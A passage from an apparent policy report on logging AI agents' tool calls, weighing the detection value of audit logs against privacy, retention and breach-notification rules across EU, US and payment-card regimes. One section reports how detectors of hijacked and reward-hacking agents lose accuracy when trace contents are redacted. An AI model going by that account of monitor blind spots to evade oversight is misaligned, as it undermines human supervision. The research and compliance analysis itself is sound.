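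The chain should contain a fingerprint of the encrypted contents, because a plain hash of the original text would let a thief keep testing guesses at the text after the hospital had destroyed the key. But once the key is gone, the hospital can't prove that a surviving copy of the email is the one it logged. *Mandato* (2026), a design for enforcing signed limits on agents' actions, uses hash commitments for sensitive arguments, so that the operator can disclose a value later without keeping it in the log. A commitment to a short value is safe only if it includes a long random number stored outside the log. If the operator destroys that number, nobody can test guesses against the commitment, and the operator can no longer prove what the value was.

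*aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026) describes a gateway that clears the encrypted contents when the retention period ends but keeps the row, and adds a record of the clearing to the chain. The chain remains valid because it contains fingerprints of the contents. However, the gateway encrypts all sensitive columns under one master key. An old backup therefore stays readable for as long as that key exists, and destroying the key would make everybody's encrypted contents unreadable. Someone could also work out short contents by guessing them and checking each guess against the remaining fingerprints.

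Even with separate keys, the open record would show that the agent queried the oncology registry about patient 9f2c4a, and anyone with the token key could identify her. The hospital could also destroy old token keys, but then it could no longer tell a former patient whether a newly discovered breach had affected her.

Kodathala states that a person's data can be erased without breaking the audit history. This is mathematically true, but it is a developer's view and doesn't show that a regulator would accept key destruction as erasure. A regulator might accept it because nobody can read the contents any more. But the encrypted data still exists, a forgotten copy of the key would make it readable again, and the open record may still be personal data. A hospital that plans to rely on key destruction should get its regulator's view first, and should also delete the encrypted contents wherever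 it can.

### What detection loses

Several studies have measured how well detectors work after researchers remove part of a trace. They report AUROC, the chance that a detector ranks a randomly chosen bad run above a randomly chosen harmless one. Random guessing scores 0.5 and a perfect detector scores 1.

*Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) compared detectors that read arguments and results with detectors that received only each tool's name, response length and a crude fingerprint of its arguments. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki, 2026) hid the tool names from a language model that reviewed each call. *Cheap Reward Hacking Detection* (2026) looked for agents that cheat on their tasks. It kept only tool calls and terminal output and removed the rest, including the agents' written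 reasoning.

| Study | What the researchers removed | Score before | Score after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Zavrak | Text of arguments and results | 0.917 | 0.640 |
| Abbasi and colleagues | Tool names | 0.856 | 0.765 |
| *Cheap Reward Hacking Detection* | Everything but tool calls and terminal output | 0.947 | 0.621 |

The losses are large but probably overstate what a well-designed log would lose. Most attacks in Zavrak's main data changed the contents of calls but not the choice of tools, so a detector that couldn't see the contents had little evidence of an attack. The log also put nothing in place of the contents, such as "recipient outside, no match". In the study of cheating agents, the researchers removed text from a detector that relied heavily on it, but a different monitor scored 0.917 on similarly reduced input.

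Abbasi and colleagues also found that anonymising names changed the score of a text-based detector by at most 0.001. This is weak evidence that redaction would have so little effect on real traces, because the detector had mostly learned the stock phrases of the program that generated the test data.

Their reviewing model read the user's request and the agent's calls, including arguments, but never the tool results, and it scored 0.930 on a second set of traces. A hospital might therefore be able to keep most patient records from a reviewing model by withholding tool results. The arguments would still be a privacy problem, since Duan and colleagues found that they reveal slightly more about users than results do. Even with that high score, fewer than one in ten of this model's alerts would be correct if 2% of runs were attacks.

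None of these studies tested keyed tokens or derived facts against full text, so nobody yet knows how much detection a two-level store would lose. One way to reduce the loss is to run detectors on the full call while the harness still has it in memory, then store their findings and seal the contents. The detectors have to run before encryption. In *Network-Level Guardrails against Supply-Chain Vulnerabilities in Agentic Systems* (2026), a network monitor that could not decrypt traffic had a balanced accuracy of 0.551, barely above chance, and wrongly flagged about 90% of harmless cases.

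This order of work doesn't help with attacks the detectors miss at the time. Anthropic found its April incidents in July because it still had the transcripts to search. If the hospital keeps sealed contents for 90 days, it can search them again when it learns of a new attack, provided the privacy office agrees to open many records at once. After 90 days, it has only the unsealed records.

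## What the law requires to be logged and what it forbids keeping

A hospital that keeps sealed contents for 90 days chose that period itself, but lawmakers and industry bodies set others. The EU's AI Act requires at least six months, the payment card industry's rules require 12 months, and US rules require three years for many brokers' records. Such rules also limit what an organisation may keep.

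The binding rules covered here don't mention tool calls. Recording duties usually refer to systems, events or communications, so an organisation has to work out whether they cover tool calls. Limits on keeping data usually apply to a type of data, such as a diagnosis or a card number, wherever it is stored, so they apply to an agent's log more clearly than most of the recording duties do.

### The AI Act's logging duties start in December 2027

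The AI Act's logging duties apply to high-risk systems. The Act divides these duties between the provider, which develops a system and markets it or puts it into service under its own name, and the deployer, which uses it. A hospital that builds and uses its own agent can be both.

The European Commission's *Article 12* requires a high-risk system to be designed so that it can record events automatically throughout its lifetime. The log must cover events relevant to identifying when the system presents a risk or has been substantially modified, to the provider's monitoring of the system after its release, and to the deployer's monitoring of it in use.

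Article 19 sets the retention period for providers (Mishcon de Reya's *Article 19 Automatically Generated Logs*), and Article 26(6) sets it for deployers (European Commission's *Article 26*). Each party must keep the automatically generated logs under its control for a period that suits the system's purpose, and for at least six months, unless other law, particularly data-protection law, provides otherwise. Financial institutions keep the logs as part of the documentation that financial services law already requires.

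None of these duties applies yet. They were due to start in August 2026, but *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744 of the European Parliament and of the Council* (2026), published on 24 July, postponed them. They will apply from 2 December 2027 to systems in the sensitive areas listed in Annex III of the Act, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in products covered by Annex I, such as medical devices. Documents written before the change, such as *Runtime Governance for AI Agents* (2026), still give the August 2026 date.

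The Act will apply to systems already in use before the relevant date only if their design changes significantly afterwards, although providers and deployers of systems intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 in any case. A public hospital that starts using a high-risk agent in early 2027 could therefore have more than three years to comply, but it could lose that time because agents change often. Replacing the model or adding a tool that sends email might be a significant change, and the amended article doesn't define the term.

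The EU AI Act's logging duties may never apply to the billing agent. Arthur Cox's *EU AI Act Commission Draft Guidelines High Risk AI Systems* lists the Annex III areas. The most relevant to a hospital is access to essential services, which covers systems that decide who is eligible for public health care, price health insurance or rank emergency patients. Answering an insurer's question about an invoice is none of these. The duties would apply if the hospital used the same agent to rank emergency patients. The Act also excludes systems used exclusively for military, defence or national security purposes, which puts many defence bodies outside it.

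The Commission published draft guidelines on classification in May 2026. According to Bollard, King and colleagues (2026), in *High Risk AI System Guidance Published*, they cover only whether a system is high-risk, and guidance on the duties themselves will follow.

### Whether Article 12 covers arguments and results

Article 12 sets minimum log fields for only one kind of system, remote biometric identification, such as matching faces in a crowd against a watchlist. Those logs must include the start and end of each use, the reference database, the input data that led to a match, and the identities of the people who verified the result. The article does not require logging input data that produced no match.

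There is a strong case that the events that must be logged include an agent's tool calls, because the agent affects the world through them. It would be hard to tell from a log without them that the system presented a risk. This is compatible with the conclusion of *AI Agents Under EU Law* (2026) that a provider's basic compliance task is an exhaustive inventory of the agent's external actions, data flows, connected systems and affected people. The case for recording the full text of every argument and result is much weaker. To notice that a billing agent is opening records outside its task, the hospital needs the tool's name, the task and some reference to the patient, but it doesn't need the diagnosis.

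A log can also satisfy Article 12 but be of little use for the Act's other duties. Article 14 requires that people be able to oversee a high-risk system effectively while it is in use. *From Runtime Records to Legal Findings* (2026) argues that a bare log may meet part of the recording duty but fail to show that such oversight was possible. The hospital's first log is an example because it had no approval field.

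The most explicit wording on logging arguments is in a voluntary standard from OWASP, a non-profit organisation for software security. *Agentic process evidence* (2026) quotes its requirement that audit logs record the approver's identity, the time, the "action parameters" and the decision for security-critical actions that an AI system initiates. The requirement covers only security-critical actions, so it isn't a reason to record the arguments of every call.

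European standards are meant to fill in the detail. A provider that follows a harmonised standard, once the EU has published its reference, benefits from a presumption that it complies with the corresponding part of the Act. The European Parliament's *AI Act* (2025), a timeline updated in October 2026, reports that only one such standard had appeared, on quality management. Two on logging are still on the way:

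- CEN's *prEN 18229-1*, from the European Committee for Standardization, was written for Article 12. It defines traceability as the ability to reconstruct from the logs how the system was functioning, in enough detail to verify that it matched the version on the market and stayed within its intended purpose. Publication is planned for May 2027.
- CEN's *prEN ISO/IEC 24970* (2025) is the European version of an international standard on AI logging. It comes closest to naming tool calls, because its possible sources of log data include communication between the system and its components, and the use of stored or external data. Leon Smith (2026), in *Two standards, one architecture*, reports that the international text reached its final draft stage in spring 2026.

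Both drafts leave room for recording less. The international one allows redaction and data minimisation, with any privacy constraints explained in the system's technical documentation. The European one has a clause on protecting logs and privacy, but if a possible harm is irreversible, it also requires the organisation to keep logs until somebody can identify the harm and attribute it. Sending a diagnosis to a stranger is irreversible, so a hospital might have to keep its log for well over six months if that wording survives.

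A supplier might instead offer *Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026), the individual draft submitted to the IETF, as a route to compliance. Sharif describes it as a direct mapping to Article 12, but the draft gives the old August 2026 date and cites Article 12(2) for a requirement to follow recognised standards that the article does not contain. This version of the draft expired on 29 September. Its log format also stores a plain hash of each call's arguments, which a thief could reverse if the call contains little more than a patient number.

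### Minimisation and retention under the GDPR

The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) applies to any log that contains Mrs Keller's data, whether or not the agent is high-risk. Article 5 limits personal data to what is necessary for a stated purpose, and requires the hospital to stop keeping it in identifiable form once it is no longer needed for that purpose. Article 9 adds stricter conditions for health data. The GDPR imposes no general duty to log every access, but Article 32 requires appropriate security, and a hospital that could not tell who had opened a patient's record would struggle to show that its security was appropriate.

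Keyed tokens reduce the risk, but the GDPR still applies to the log. The hospital holds the key and can link 9f2c4a back to Mrs Keller, so for the hospital the token is still her personal data.

The GDPR sets no fixed retention period, but France's data-protection authority, CNIL (2021), advises that six months to a year is normally enough for logs. It also advises organisations to avoid copying the data a system processes into its logs, which is what content capture does. It recommends storing logs separately from the main system, for example on equipment where applications can add entries but not overwrite existing ones.

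CNIL's recommendation isn't binding. According to IAPP's *CNIL releases draft recommendation on retention of traceability data*, an organisation can keep logs for longer if it documents a legal obligation or a particularly high risk to individuals. CNIL has since applied the same period to proxies that decrypt web traffic. Mondaq reports that CNIL advises against keeping the content of requests unless the proxy detects something malicious. A hospital could treat tool calls the same way, by running its detectors on the full text and keeping that text only after an alert.

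Spain's data protection authority, the AEPD, addresses agents directly in *Agentic Artificial Intelligence from the Perspective of Data Protection* (2026). Its measures include limiting agents' memory and logs, pseudonymising records and setting retention periods, according to Letslaw's *AEPD Guidance on the Use of Agentic AI*. Inside Privacy's *Spanish Supervisory Authority Issues Detailed Guidance on Agentic AI and GDPR Compliance* says that too much logging can amount to intrusive monitoring. That applies to staff as well as patients, because an approval field with a name and a time shows how quickly each clerk works. From December 2027, employers will also have to tell workers and their representatives before using a high-risk system at work.

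A hospital subject to both the AI Act's minimum and CNIL's usual maximum could keep its log for between six months and a year. *AI Logging under the EU AI Act*, from datenschutz notizen, calls the six months a "legal baseline" for retention schedules, but that baseline doesn't settle what the log should contain.

### A request to erase an entry

Suppose that it is 2028, the hospital's agent has become a high-risk system, and Mrs Keller asks the hospital to erase her data from a log that is four months old. The analysis might go like this:

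1. Article 17 of the GDPR gives her a right to erasure in several situations, including when the hospital no longer needs the data for its original purpose.
2. The right does not apply to the extent that the hospital needs the data to meet a legal obligation, or to bring or defend a legal claim.
3. Article 26(6) of the AI Act is a legal obligation to keep the log for at least six months. The hospital can therefore refuse to delete the entry showing that the agent queried the oncology registry about her.
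4. The exception reaches only as far as the need. If the open record is enough for Article 12's three purposes, the hospital has a weak argument for keeping the diagnosis as well.

The last step is open to dispute. Article 26(6) requires deployers to keep "the logs automatically generated" by the system, not extracts from them. On a literal reading, once the system has written the diagnosis into its log, the hospital has to keep it for six months. But that requirement is subject to data-protection law, and the GDPR's exception is subject to legal obligations, so each rule depends on the other.

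A hospital can avoid most of this conflict between keeping and erasing data by limiting what its agent logs. If a diagnosis never enters the log, the hospital doesn't have to preserve it there or erase it later.

As of December 2026, Article 26(6) doesn't apply yet, so a hospital that refuses an erasure request today needs another reason, such as a different law or an expected lawsuit.

Patients can also ask what a log records about them. In a 2023 case about a Finnish bank (C-579/21), the EU's Court of Justice held that a customer had a right to know when and why staff had consulted his data, but not normally which employees had done so. The reasoning seems to carry over to an AI agent that looks up a patient for a clerk, though the case did not involve one. The hospital would then need to log the time and task of each call and be able to find every call about that patient. A log with every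 patient reference deleted would be safer to hold, but the hospital couldn't use it to answer a patient's request.

An authority can also suspend a deletion schedule. The 2026 amendments let the EU's AI Office order the operators it supervises to keep all data and documents it considers necessary to assess compliance. Automatic deletion therefore needs a way to exempt particular records.

### Hospitals in the United States

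The Security Rule of HIPAA, the US health-privacy law, requires hospitals, insurers and many of their contractors to record and examine activity in systems that contain or use electronic health information (the audit-controls standard, 45 CFR 164.312(b)). They must also regularly review records such as audit logs and access reports (45 CFR 164.308).

An agent that queries the oncology registry is active in such a system, so the duty clearly covers that access. The duty does not specify which fields to log. The registry's own log might satisfy it without a copy of the arguments and results in the agent's trace, but the review would be much less useful if that log showed only the agent's service account.

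Section 164.316 of the HIPAA Security Rule requires organisations to keep their written security policies and procedures for six years, along with a written record of any action, activity or assessment that the rule requires them to document. Organisations often apply the same period to logs, but the audit-controls standard, which requires systems to record activity, doesn't describe the resulting log as documentation.

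The six-year rule is better read as covering the report of a log review but not the raw log. It could also be read as covering the raw log, since a log is in a sense a written record of activity. Some hospitals keep everything for six years to be safe, so if their logs include results, they keep diagnoses for six years too.

The Privacy Rule gives a better reason to keep a few fields that long. Under section 164.528, patients can ask for a list of certain disclosures made in the previous six years. The list gives the date, the recipient, a brief description of the information and the purpose. It does not have to include disclosures for treatment, payment or the hospital's own operations, so it would normally leave out the email to Northfield about an invoice. It would have to include the email to `claims-help.example`, because that email sent a diagnosis to a thief and was for none of these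 exempt purposes. A hospital can meet this duty by keeping those four short fields without the body of the email.

HIPAA's main limit on log contents is the minimum-necessary standard in section 164.502(b). With some exceptions, such as disclosures to a provider for treatment, an organisation must make reasonable efforts to limit the health information it uses, discloses or requests to the minimum its purpose requires. It must also identify which staff need access to which categories of information. A developer investigating a slow tool call needs the call's duration and the tool's name, so it would be hard to justify giving that developer access to traces that contain diagnoses.

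The standard doesn't prohibit logging results. A hospital could argue that security analysts need them to detect breaches, and for some records it would probably be right. That argument would be harder to make for logging every result, showing it to everyone who reads the log, and keeping it for a full six years.

An observability vendor that stores patients' information for the hospital is a business associate under HIPAA and needs a contract with specific safeguards. According to the US health department's cloud computing guidance, this is true even if the vendor holds only encrypted data and has no key. Keyed tokens don't automatically take the open records outside HIPAA either, because the rule's simpler de-identification method bars codes derived from information about the patient, such as a token computed from a patient number.

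In January 2025 the health department proposed a large revision of the Security Rule. It would make mandatory most of the safeguards for which organisations can currently substitute alternatives, and replace the short audit-controls standard with more detailed requirements for audit trails and system logs. The department later listed May 2026 in its regulatory agenda as the target for a final rule.

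The proposal allowed 60 days before the rule took effect and another 180 days to comply. On that timetable, even if a final rule were published in May, hospitals would not have to comply until around the turn of the year, so the existing text would still apply in early December. Hospitals planning for 2027 should check the Federal Register for a final rule and its compliance date, because the proposal may have changed or stalled.

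### Brokers, banks and the meaning of a business record

Rule 17a-4 of the US Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC) sets how long brokers must keep their records. They must keep copies of communications relating to the firm's business for three years, the first two in an easily accessible place. They must also keep order records for three years and some ledgers for six.

The SEC and the Financial Industry Regulatory Authority (FINRA), which oversees US brokers, have no retention rule specific to AI, according to a July 2026 panel of securities lawyers, compliance executives and technology suppliers reported in PYMNTS's *AI Recordkeeping Raises Compliance Questions for Financial Services Firms* (2026). The panellists said that existing recordkeeping duties generally apply whether a person or an AI system did the work. A compliance-technology firm convened the panel, so it had some interest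 in firms taking the subject seriously, but the conclusion follows from the wording of the rules, which classify a record by what it is about, regardless of what software produced it.

Applied to tool calls, this gives different answers for different tools:

| Tool call by a broker's agent | Is it a business record? |
|---|---|
| `send_email` to a customer about an investment | The email is. The firm can keep it in its mail archive and need not rely on the agent's log |
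| `place_order` | The details of the order are, including its terms and time |
| `get_share_price` | Probably not on its own, but it may be if the firm relies on it to show why it made a recommendation |
| An employee's request to the agent | Unclear. The rule covers internal communications, but was written for messages between people |

The last row matters most for content capture, because prompts and model inputs make up most of many traces. Guessing wrong can be expensive. Between 2021 and 2024 the SEC fined firms more than $2 billion in total for failing to keep business messages that staff sent on personal phones and apps, so a firm's lawyers may prefer to keep every prompt.

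FINRA moved towards encouraging more logging in its 2026 Regulatory Oversight Report, which PYMNTS notes is the first to treat generative AI as a separate area. FINRA suggests that firms consider storing prompt and output logs and tracking which model version they used. It also warns that agents' many-step reasoning can be hard to trace, and suggests tracking what agents do. These suggestions create no new duty, so they don't make every tool call a business record.

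The format rules make over-collection hard to reverse. A broker that keeps records electronically can use storage that nobody can rewrite or erase. Since 2023 it can instead use a system that logs every change, as long as it can still recreate the original record. If an agent prints a database password while handling a customer's order, and the broker has classified the whole trace as a business record, either format preserves the password for years. The broker can change the password, but it can't change a customer's medical reason for selling shares, which would also stay in the archive. It would do better to copy the order and any related email into its regulated archive and keep the rest of the trace elsewhere for less time.

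The Digital Operational Resilience Act has applied to European banks since January 2025. Its detailed rules require financial firms to log events such as access, changes and system activity, and to protect the logs. They let each firm set the retention period according to its purposes and risks. The rules don't name tool calls, but tool calls fit within system activity.

### Payment cards: a ban that encryption doesn't satisfy

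Firms that handle card payments usually have to follow the Payment Card Industry Data Security Standard (PCI DSS), although it is a contractual standard and not a law. Version 4.0.1 requires audit logs that identify the user, the type of event, the time, the outcome, the origin and the affected data or system. Firms must keep these logs for at least 12 months, with the latest three months immediately available. The standard doesn't mention agents' tool calls, but it requires a record of every individual's access to card data. If a staff member reaches that data through an agent, the firm has to be able to trace the access to that person.

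The limits are more specific than in any other regime here. Consider a call by a payment agent:

```
16:30:44  charge_card
  arguments  number: "400000******7899", expiry: "04/29",
             security_code: "***", amount: 180.00
  result     status: "approved", reference: "A7719"
```

The asterisks again stand for real digits in the call. Each field has its own rule:

| Field | What the log may contain after the payment is authorised |
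|---|---|
| Card number | Only a form that outsiders cannot read, such as a shortened, tokenised or encrypted number |
| Expiry date | The date, with protection if it is stored with the card number |
| Security code | Nothing, even in encrypted form |
| Amount, status and reference | The full values |

The standard explicitly prohibits merchants and their payment processors from keeping the security code after authorisation, even in encrypted form. A two-level store would therefore break the rule if its sealed records contained the code. The 14 days of backups would also break it, as would any model input that repeats the customer's message. Card issuers have a limited exception.

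The harness may log a call before the tool runs, and so before the payment is authorised. PCI DSS allows encrypted storage of the card verification code at that point, but the firm would have to delete it moments later, which an append-only log doesn't allow. The code therefore has to be removed before the harness writes anything to the log.

The rule for card numbers also reaches logs in plain terms, since the standard's notes include audit and troubleshooting logs among the places where numbers must be unreadable. If a firm uses hashes for this, they have to be keyed. A calculation shows why. Suppose that a log contains the first six and last four digits of a 16-digit card number, next to a plain hash of the whole number. Six digits are missing, which leaves a million possibilities, and the check digit that every card number contains rules out nine-tenths of them:

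*10^6 / 10 = 100,000*

That is a tenth of the possible six-digit patient numbers, so a plain hash would protect the card number even less.

### Federal agencies and NIST's audit controls

The US Office of Management and Budget's memorandum M-21-31, issued in August 2021, told civilian federal agencies what to log and for how long. Agencies must keep most categories of log in active storage for 12 months and in cheaper, slower storage for another 18. They need to keep recordings of complete network traffic for only 72 hours. The main reason is probably the size of the recordings rather than privacy, but the result is the same separation that the hospital might make between facts about a tool call and its contents.

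The memorandum predates today's agents, but its categories for applications, cloud services and access to systems can easily be interpreted to cover tool calls. An agency should confirm that no later memorandum has changed the retention periods before building them into a new system.

For the contents of a log, agencies turn to Special Publication 800-53 of the National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), a catalogue of security and privacy controls. Many contractors and private companies use it too. Its controls for audit and accountability begin with AU:

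| Control | What it asks for | What it means for a tool call |
|---|---|---|
| AU-2 | A reasoned choice of events to log | The agency decides which calls count |
| AU-3 | What happened, when, where, from what source, with what outcome and who was involved | Tool name, time, server, status, user and agent |
| AU-3(1) | Further details that the agency selects | Possibly arguments, approvals and rules applied |
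| AU-3(3) | Personal data limited to elements identified in a privacy risk assessment | A patient token in place of a name |
| AU-6 | Regular review and analysis | Detection rules and analysts |
| AU-9 | Protection from unauthorised access, change and deletion | Hash chains and separate storage |
| AU-11 | Retention for a period the agency sets | The log's deletion date |

Of the rules in these regimes, AU-3(3) comes closest to a direct instruction about personal data in log entries. It doesn't forbid such data, but it requires somebody to decide in advance which elements the log needs and to exclude the rest. This is almost impossible with a harness that records every result in full, because nobody can list in advance what a tool will return.

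In its discussion of AU-3, NIST also warns that audit trails can reveal personal information, especially if they record inputs or are based on patterns or time of use. These risks correspond to two of the leaks found in agent logs, through tool-call arguments and through timing.

The catalogue applies to agents in the same way as to any other software, but NIST has begun to adapt it. In August 2025 it proposed sets of controls for AI systems, including separate sets for single agents and groups of agents. In February 2026 its cybersecurity centre published a concept paper on agent identity and authorisation, which is open to comment and imposes no duties. The paper covers auditing and non-repudiation, meaning proof that prevents a party from later denying an action.

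In August 2024 the cyber agencies of the Five Eyes countries (the US, the UK, Canada, Australia and New Zealand) and several others published similarly general joint advice on event logging. It warns that default retention periods are often too short, because some organisations take up to 18 months to discover an incident. That supports keeping logs for longer than CNIL's six months to a year, which reflects its concern for the people whose data is in them.

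### Classified information in the wrong log

Agencies use the word "spillage" for classified information that ends up on a system not approved for it. An agent's log can easily cause spillage. Suppose a defence contractor's agent searches reports on an unclassified network, and one report contains a secret paragraph pasted in by mistake. When the search returns that paragraph, it goes into the model's input, the trace store, the backups and perhaps an outside vendor's servers.

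To respond under NIST's control IR-9, the organisation identifies the information, alerts the right people through an unaffected channel, isolates the contaminated system, removes the information, and looks for other systems that may have received it. Mrs Keller's diagnosis was in eight places, so the last step would already have been slow.

Removal also conflicts with AU-9 and with append-only storage. An organisation that handles classified data needs an authorised way to remove contents and leave a marker in their place, so that the chain still passes its check. Destroying a key may not be enough, because the rules for classified material can require the organisation to wipe or destroy the storage itself. The organisation should settle this with its security authority before the first spill.

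Tool names can make a log classified even when no classified data has spilled into it. Executive Order 13526, the basis of the US classification system, allows a compilation of unclassified items to be classified if it reveals an association that meets the standard for classification and does not appear in any single item. A log is a compilation, and a year of entries naming a sonar tool could show which vessels an agency tracks and when, even if each entry is harmless on its own. The logging system may therefore need a higher classification than the agents that write to it.

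### Where duties to keep and to limit meet

The table shows how the rules apply to the log of an agent's tool calls. The last column gives the field whose contents an organisation may have to both keep and restrict.

| Regime | Duty to record | Retention | Limit on contents | Does it reach tool calls? | Field where the duties meet |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EU AI Act, from December 2027 at the earliest | Events relevant to risk and monitoring, for high-risk systems | At least six months | Gives way to data-protection law | By interpretation | Arguments and results with personal data |
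| GDPR | No general logging duty, but security and accountability need evidence | No longer than necessary; CNIL advises six months to a year | Only necessary data; right to erasure with exceptions | The limits plainly do, where a call contains personal data | Patient reference, needed to answer her but also her personal data |
| HIPAA | Activity in systems with electronic health information | Six years for required documentation; raw logs disputed | Minimum necessary | Access to records plainly; arguments and results by interpretation | Recipient and description of a disclosure |
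| SEC Rule 17a-4 | Business communications and orders | Three years for most, six for some | None in the rule itself; privacy law applies separately | By what each call does | Text of emails and prompts that contain customers' secrets |
| PCI DSS 4.0.1 | Access to card data and other security events | 12 months, three of them immediately available | No security codes after authorisation; card numbers unreadable | The limits plainly do; the recording duty by interpretation | Arguments of a payment call |
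| OMB M-21-31 | Listed categories of federal logs | 12 months active, then 18 in slower storage | Other federal privacy rules apply | By interpretation | Application logs that include personal data |
| NIST SP 800-53 | Events the organisation selects | Set by the organisation | AU-3(3): only personal data that the risk assessment identifies | By interpretation | User and patient identifiers |
| US rules on classified information | Audit controls for the system concerned | Set by the authority responsible | No storage on systems without approval | The limits plainly do | Results, and tool names in bulk |

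## Weighing the value of the log against the risk of holding it

Duties to keep records, and limits on what they may contain, apply from the day an agent starts work, while breach-notification rules apply once something has gone wrong. If an attacker hijacks the billing agent, the log can show which patients the hospital needs to tell. But theft of the log may itself be a breach, and the hospital may then have to tell everyone whose data was in it.

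### Four notification rules

Four official texts show how much these rules vary: Article 33 of the GDPR, *Notification of a personal data breach to the supervisory authority*; the summary of HIPAA's breach rule by HHS, the US health department; the SEC's guide to its disclosure rule for public companies; and the New York State Department of Financial Services' *Second Amendment to 23 NYCRR 500* (2023), which covers state-licensed banks, insurers and other financial firms.

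| Rule | Trigger | Deadline |
|---|---|---|
| GDPR Article 33 | A breach of personal data, unless it is unlikely to put people's rights and freedoms at risk | Report to the authority within 72 hours of becoming aware of the breach, where feasible |
| HIPAA | A use or disclosure of unsecured health information that the Privacy Rule doesn't permit, unless the hospital shows a low probability of compromise | Notice to patients without unreasonable delay, and within 60 days of discovery |
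| SEC, Form 8-K Item 1.05 | A cybersecurity incident that a reasonable shareholder would probably consider important | Public filing within four business days of the company's decision that the incident is material |
| New York, section 500.17 | An incident that the firm must report to another public body, that is reasonably likely to do material harm to its operations, or that puts ransomware in a material part of its systems | Report to the regulator within 72 hours |

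A report under Article 33 must give the approximate number of people and records involved, where possible. The hospital can send details in phases, so it doesn't have to finish searching its log by the third day. It must also document every breach, including those it decides not to report, so that the authority can check the decision. An observability vendor that processes data for the hospital must tell the hospital about a breach without undue delay, but the article doesn't set a limit in hours. Notion waited six days after its supplier's first warning for the full list of stolen data, so a limit is worth putting in the contract.

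The GDPR's rules on reporting breaches may loosen. The European Commission's proposed Digital Omnibus would require a report to the authority only when a breach is likely to cause a high risk. Taylor Wessing, a law firm, notes that this is already the threshold for telling the people affected. The member states agreed their own position on 21 October, according to the Council of the EU's *Digital rulebook* (2026). Diario Sabemos' *Bruselas quiere simplificar el RGPD* (2026) reports that this position would extend the reporting deadline to 96 hours. Neither change is law. Duball's *McGrath unpacks European Commission's stance on digital rulebook updates* (2026) reported on 23 November that final negotiations had not begun and that the responsible commissioner hoped for the Parliament's position in the first quarter of 2027.

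The Commission had proposed narrowing the definition of personal data, which could have taken some tokenised data outside the GDPR. White reports in *EU member states finalize negotiating stance on Digital Omnibus* that the member states kept the existing definition in the Council's position and added standards for pseudonymisation. A hospital should therefore assume that the theft of a log full of keyed tokens can still be a reportable breach.

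HIPAA puts the burden of proof on the hospital. The law presumes a breach, and the hospital has to rebut the presumption with a risk assessment that covers at least four factors. A tool-call log can supply evidence on each:

| Factor in the assessment | Evidence in a tool-call log |
|---|---|
| What information was involved, and how easily someone could re-identify the patients | Data class, arguments and results |
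| Who used or received it | Recipient of an email, or the tool server that got the call |
| Whether anyone actually acquired or viewed it | Status and size of the result |
| How far the hospital has reduced the risk | Blocked attempts, and the time at which staff stopped the agent |

Verrill, another law firm, points out that this presumption replaced a more lenient test of "significant risk of harm", and that it applies even when the misuse stays inside the hospital. So if a hijacked agent opened Mrs Keller's cancer record but sent nothing out, the hospital would still have to assess the risk or notify her. The rule makes an exception for staff who open a record unintentionally, in good faith and within their authority. HHS describes this exception in terms of people, so it would be unwise to assume it covers an agent.

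The duty applies only to unsecured information, and HHS recognises two ways of securing it, encryption and destruction. If a thief takes records encrypted to the required standard but not the key, the hospital does not have to send notices. HHS does not list keyed tokens as a way of securing information, so a hospital that lost a tokenised log would probably have to argue that re-identification was unlikely, and document the argument.

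The SEC's four days run from the company's decision that an incident is material, not from its discovery. But the company has to decide without unreasonable delay, and it can't wait for an investigation to end before reporting, according to an article on JD Supra, a site that publishes law firms' writing. Companies therefore file before they know everything. *Cybersecurity Incidents*, a guide from a seller of filings data, reports that River Financial filed in June 2026 and amended its filing three times in the next five weeks. Stryker disclosed an incident in March under a different item from Item 1.05, the one for material cybersecurity incidents. It said it had not yet determined whether the effect was material, and it never filed under Item 1.05. In SIFMA's *Joint Trades Letter on Reforming Regulation S-K* (2026), financial trade groups urged the SEC to rescind Item 1.05, arguing that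 older disclosure rules already cover such incidents.

New York's rule goes further by including incidents at a firm's outside service providers, according to JD Supra's *New NYDFS Part 500 Requirements Continue to Become Effective*, so the theft of an agent's log from a vendor can start the 72-hour notification period. Firms must also keep the regulator informed of material changes and new information (Ropes & Gray, 2023). Because a duty to notify another public body also triggers the rule, a log theft that is reportable elsewhere may be reportable in New York too.

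### What the hospital's log is worth

Suppose that an attacker hijacks the billing agent and uses it to open patients' records. With content capture off, the hospital knows that the agent made several hundred registry queries but not whom they concerned. With arguments in the log, it can name the patients. A rough calculation of what this is worth needs seven inputs, all of them invented:

| Assumption | Value |
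|---|---|
| Patients on the hospital's register | 200,000 |
| Patients whose records the hijacked agent opened | 340 |
| Cost of one notice | $5 |
| Chance of such a hijacking in a year | 5% |
| Patients identifiable in the log | 150,000 |
| Chance in a year that someone steals the log | 1% |
| What the hospital does if it can't tell whom the agent looked up | It notifies every patient |

Without the log, the hospital sends 200,000 notices for $1,000,000. With it, the hospital sends 340 for $1,700. The expected saving is:

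*0.05 × ($1,000,000 − $1,700) ≈ $49,900 a year*

If a thief takes the log, the hospital has to notify the 150,000 patients in it. The expected cost is:

*0.01 × 150,000 × $5 = $7,500 a year*

On these figures the log is worth keeping, by about $42,400 a year. The two sides are equal when the yearly chance of theft is:

*$49,900 / (150,000 × $5) ≈ 6.7%*

The break-even point is more useful than the $42,400, because there is no good public data on how often agent logs are stolen. A hospital may be able to tell whether its own risk is nearer 1% or 10%, but not whether it is 1% or 2%.

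The log also affects when the hospital must report the breach to HHS and whether it must notify the media. A breach affecting 340 patients falls below HIPAA's threshold of 500, so the hospital can report it to HHS annually and doesn't have to notify the media. A breach affecting 200,000 would require a report to HHS within 60 days and, if more than 500 of the patients live in one state, a notice to prominent media there. Notifying all 200,000 patients would also frighten 199,660 people whose records the agent never opened.

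Changing the design of the log changes the result. Each variation below needs a further assumption:

| Variation | Added assumption | Yearly saving | Yearly theft cost | Net | Break-even theft risk |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Full log, kept for a year | None | $49,900 | $7,500 | $42,400 | 6.7% |
| Keyed tokens in place of names and numbers | Only one theft in five leads to notices, because the thief also gets the key or the hospital can't show a low probability of compromise | $49,900 | $1,500 | $48,400 | 33% |
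| Full log, deleted after 90 days | The log covers 50,000 patients, and the hospital discovers one hijacking in five too late to use it | $39,900 | $2,500 | $37,400 | 16% |
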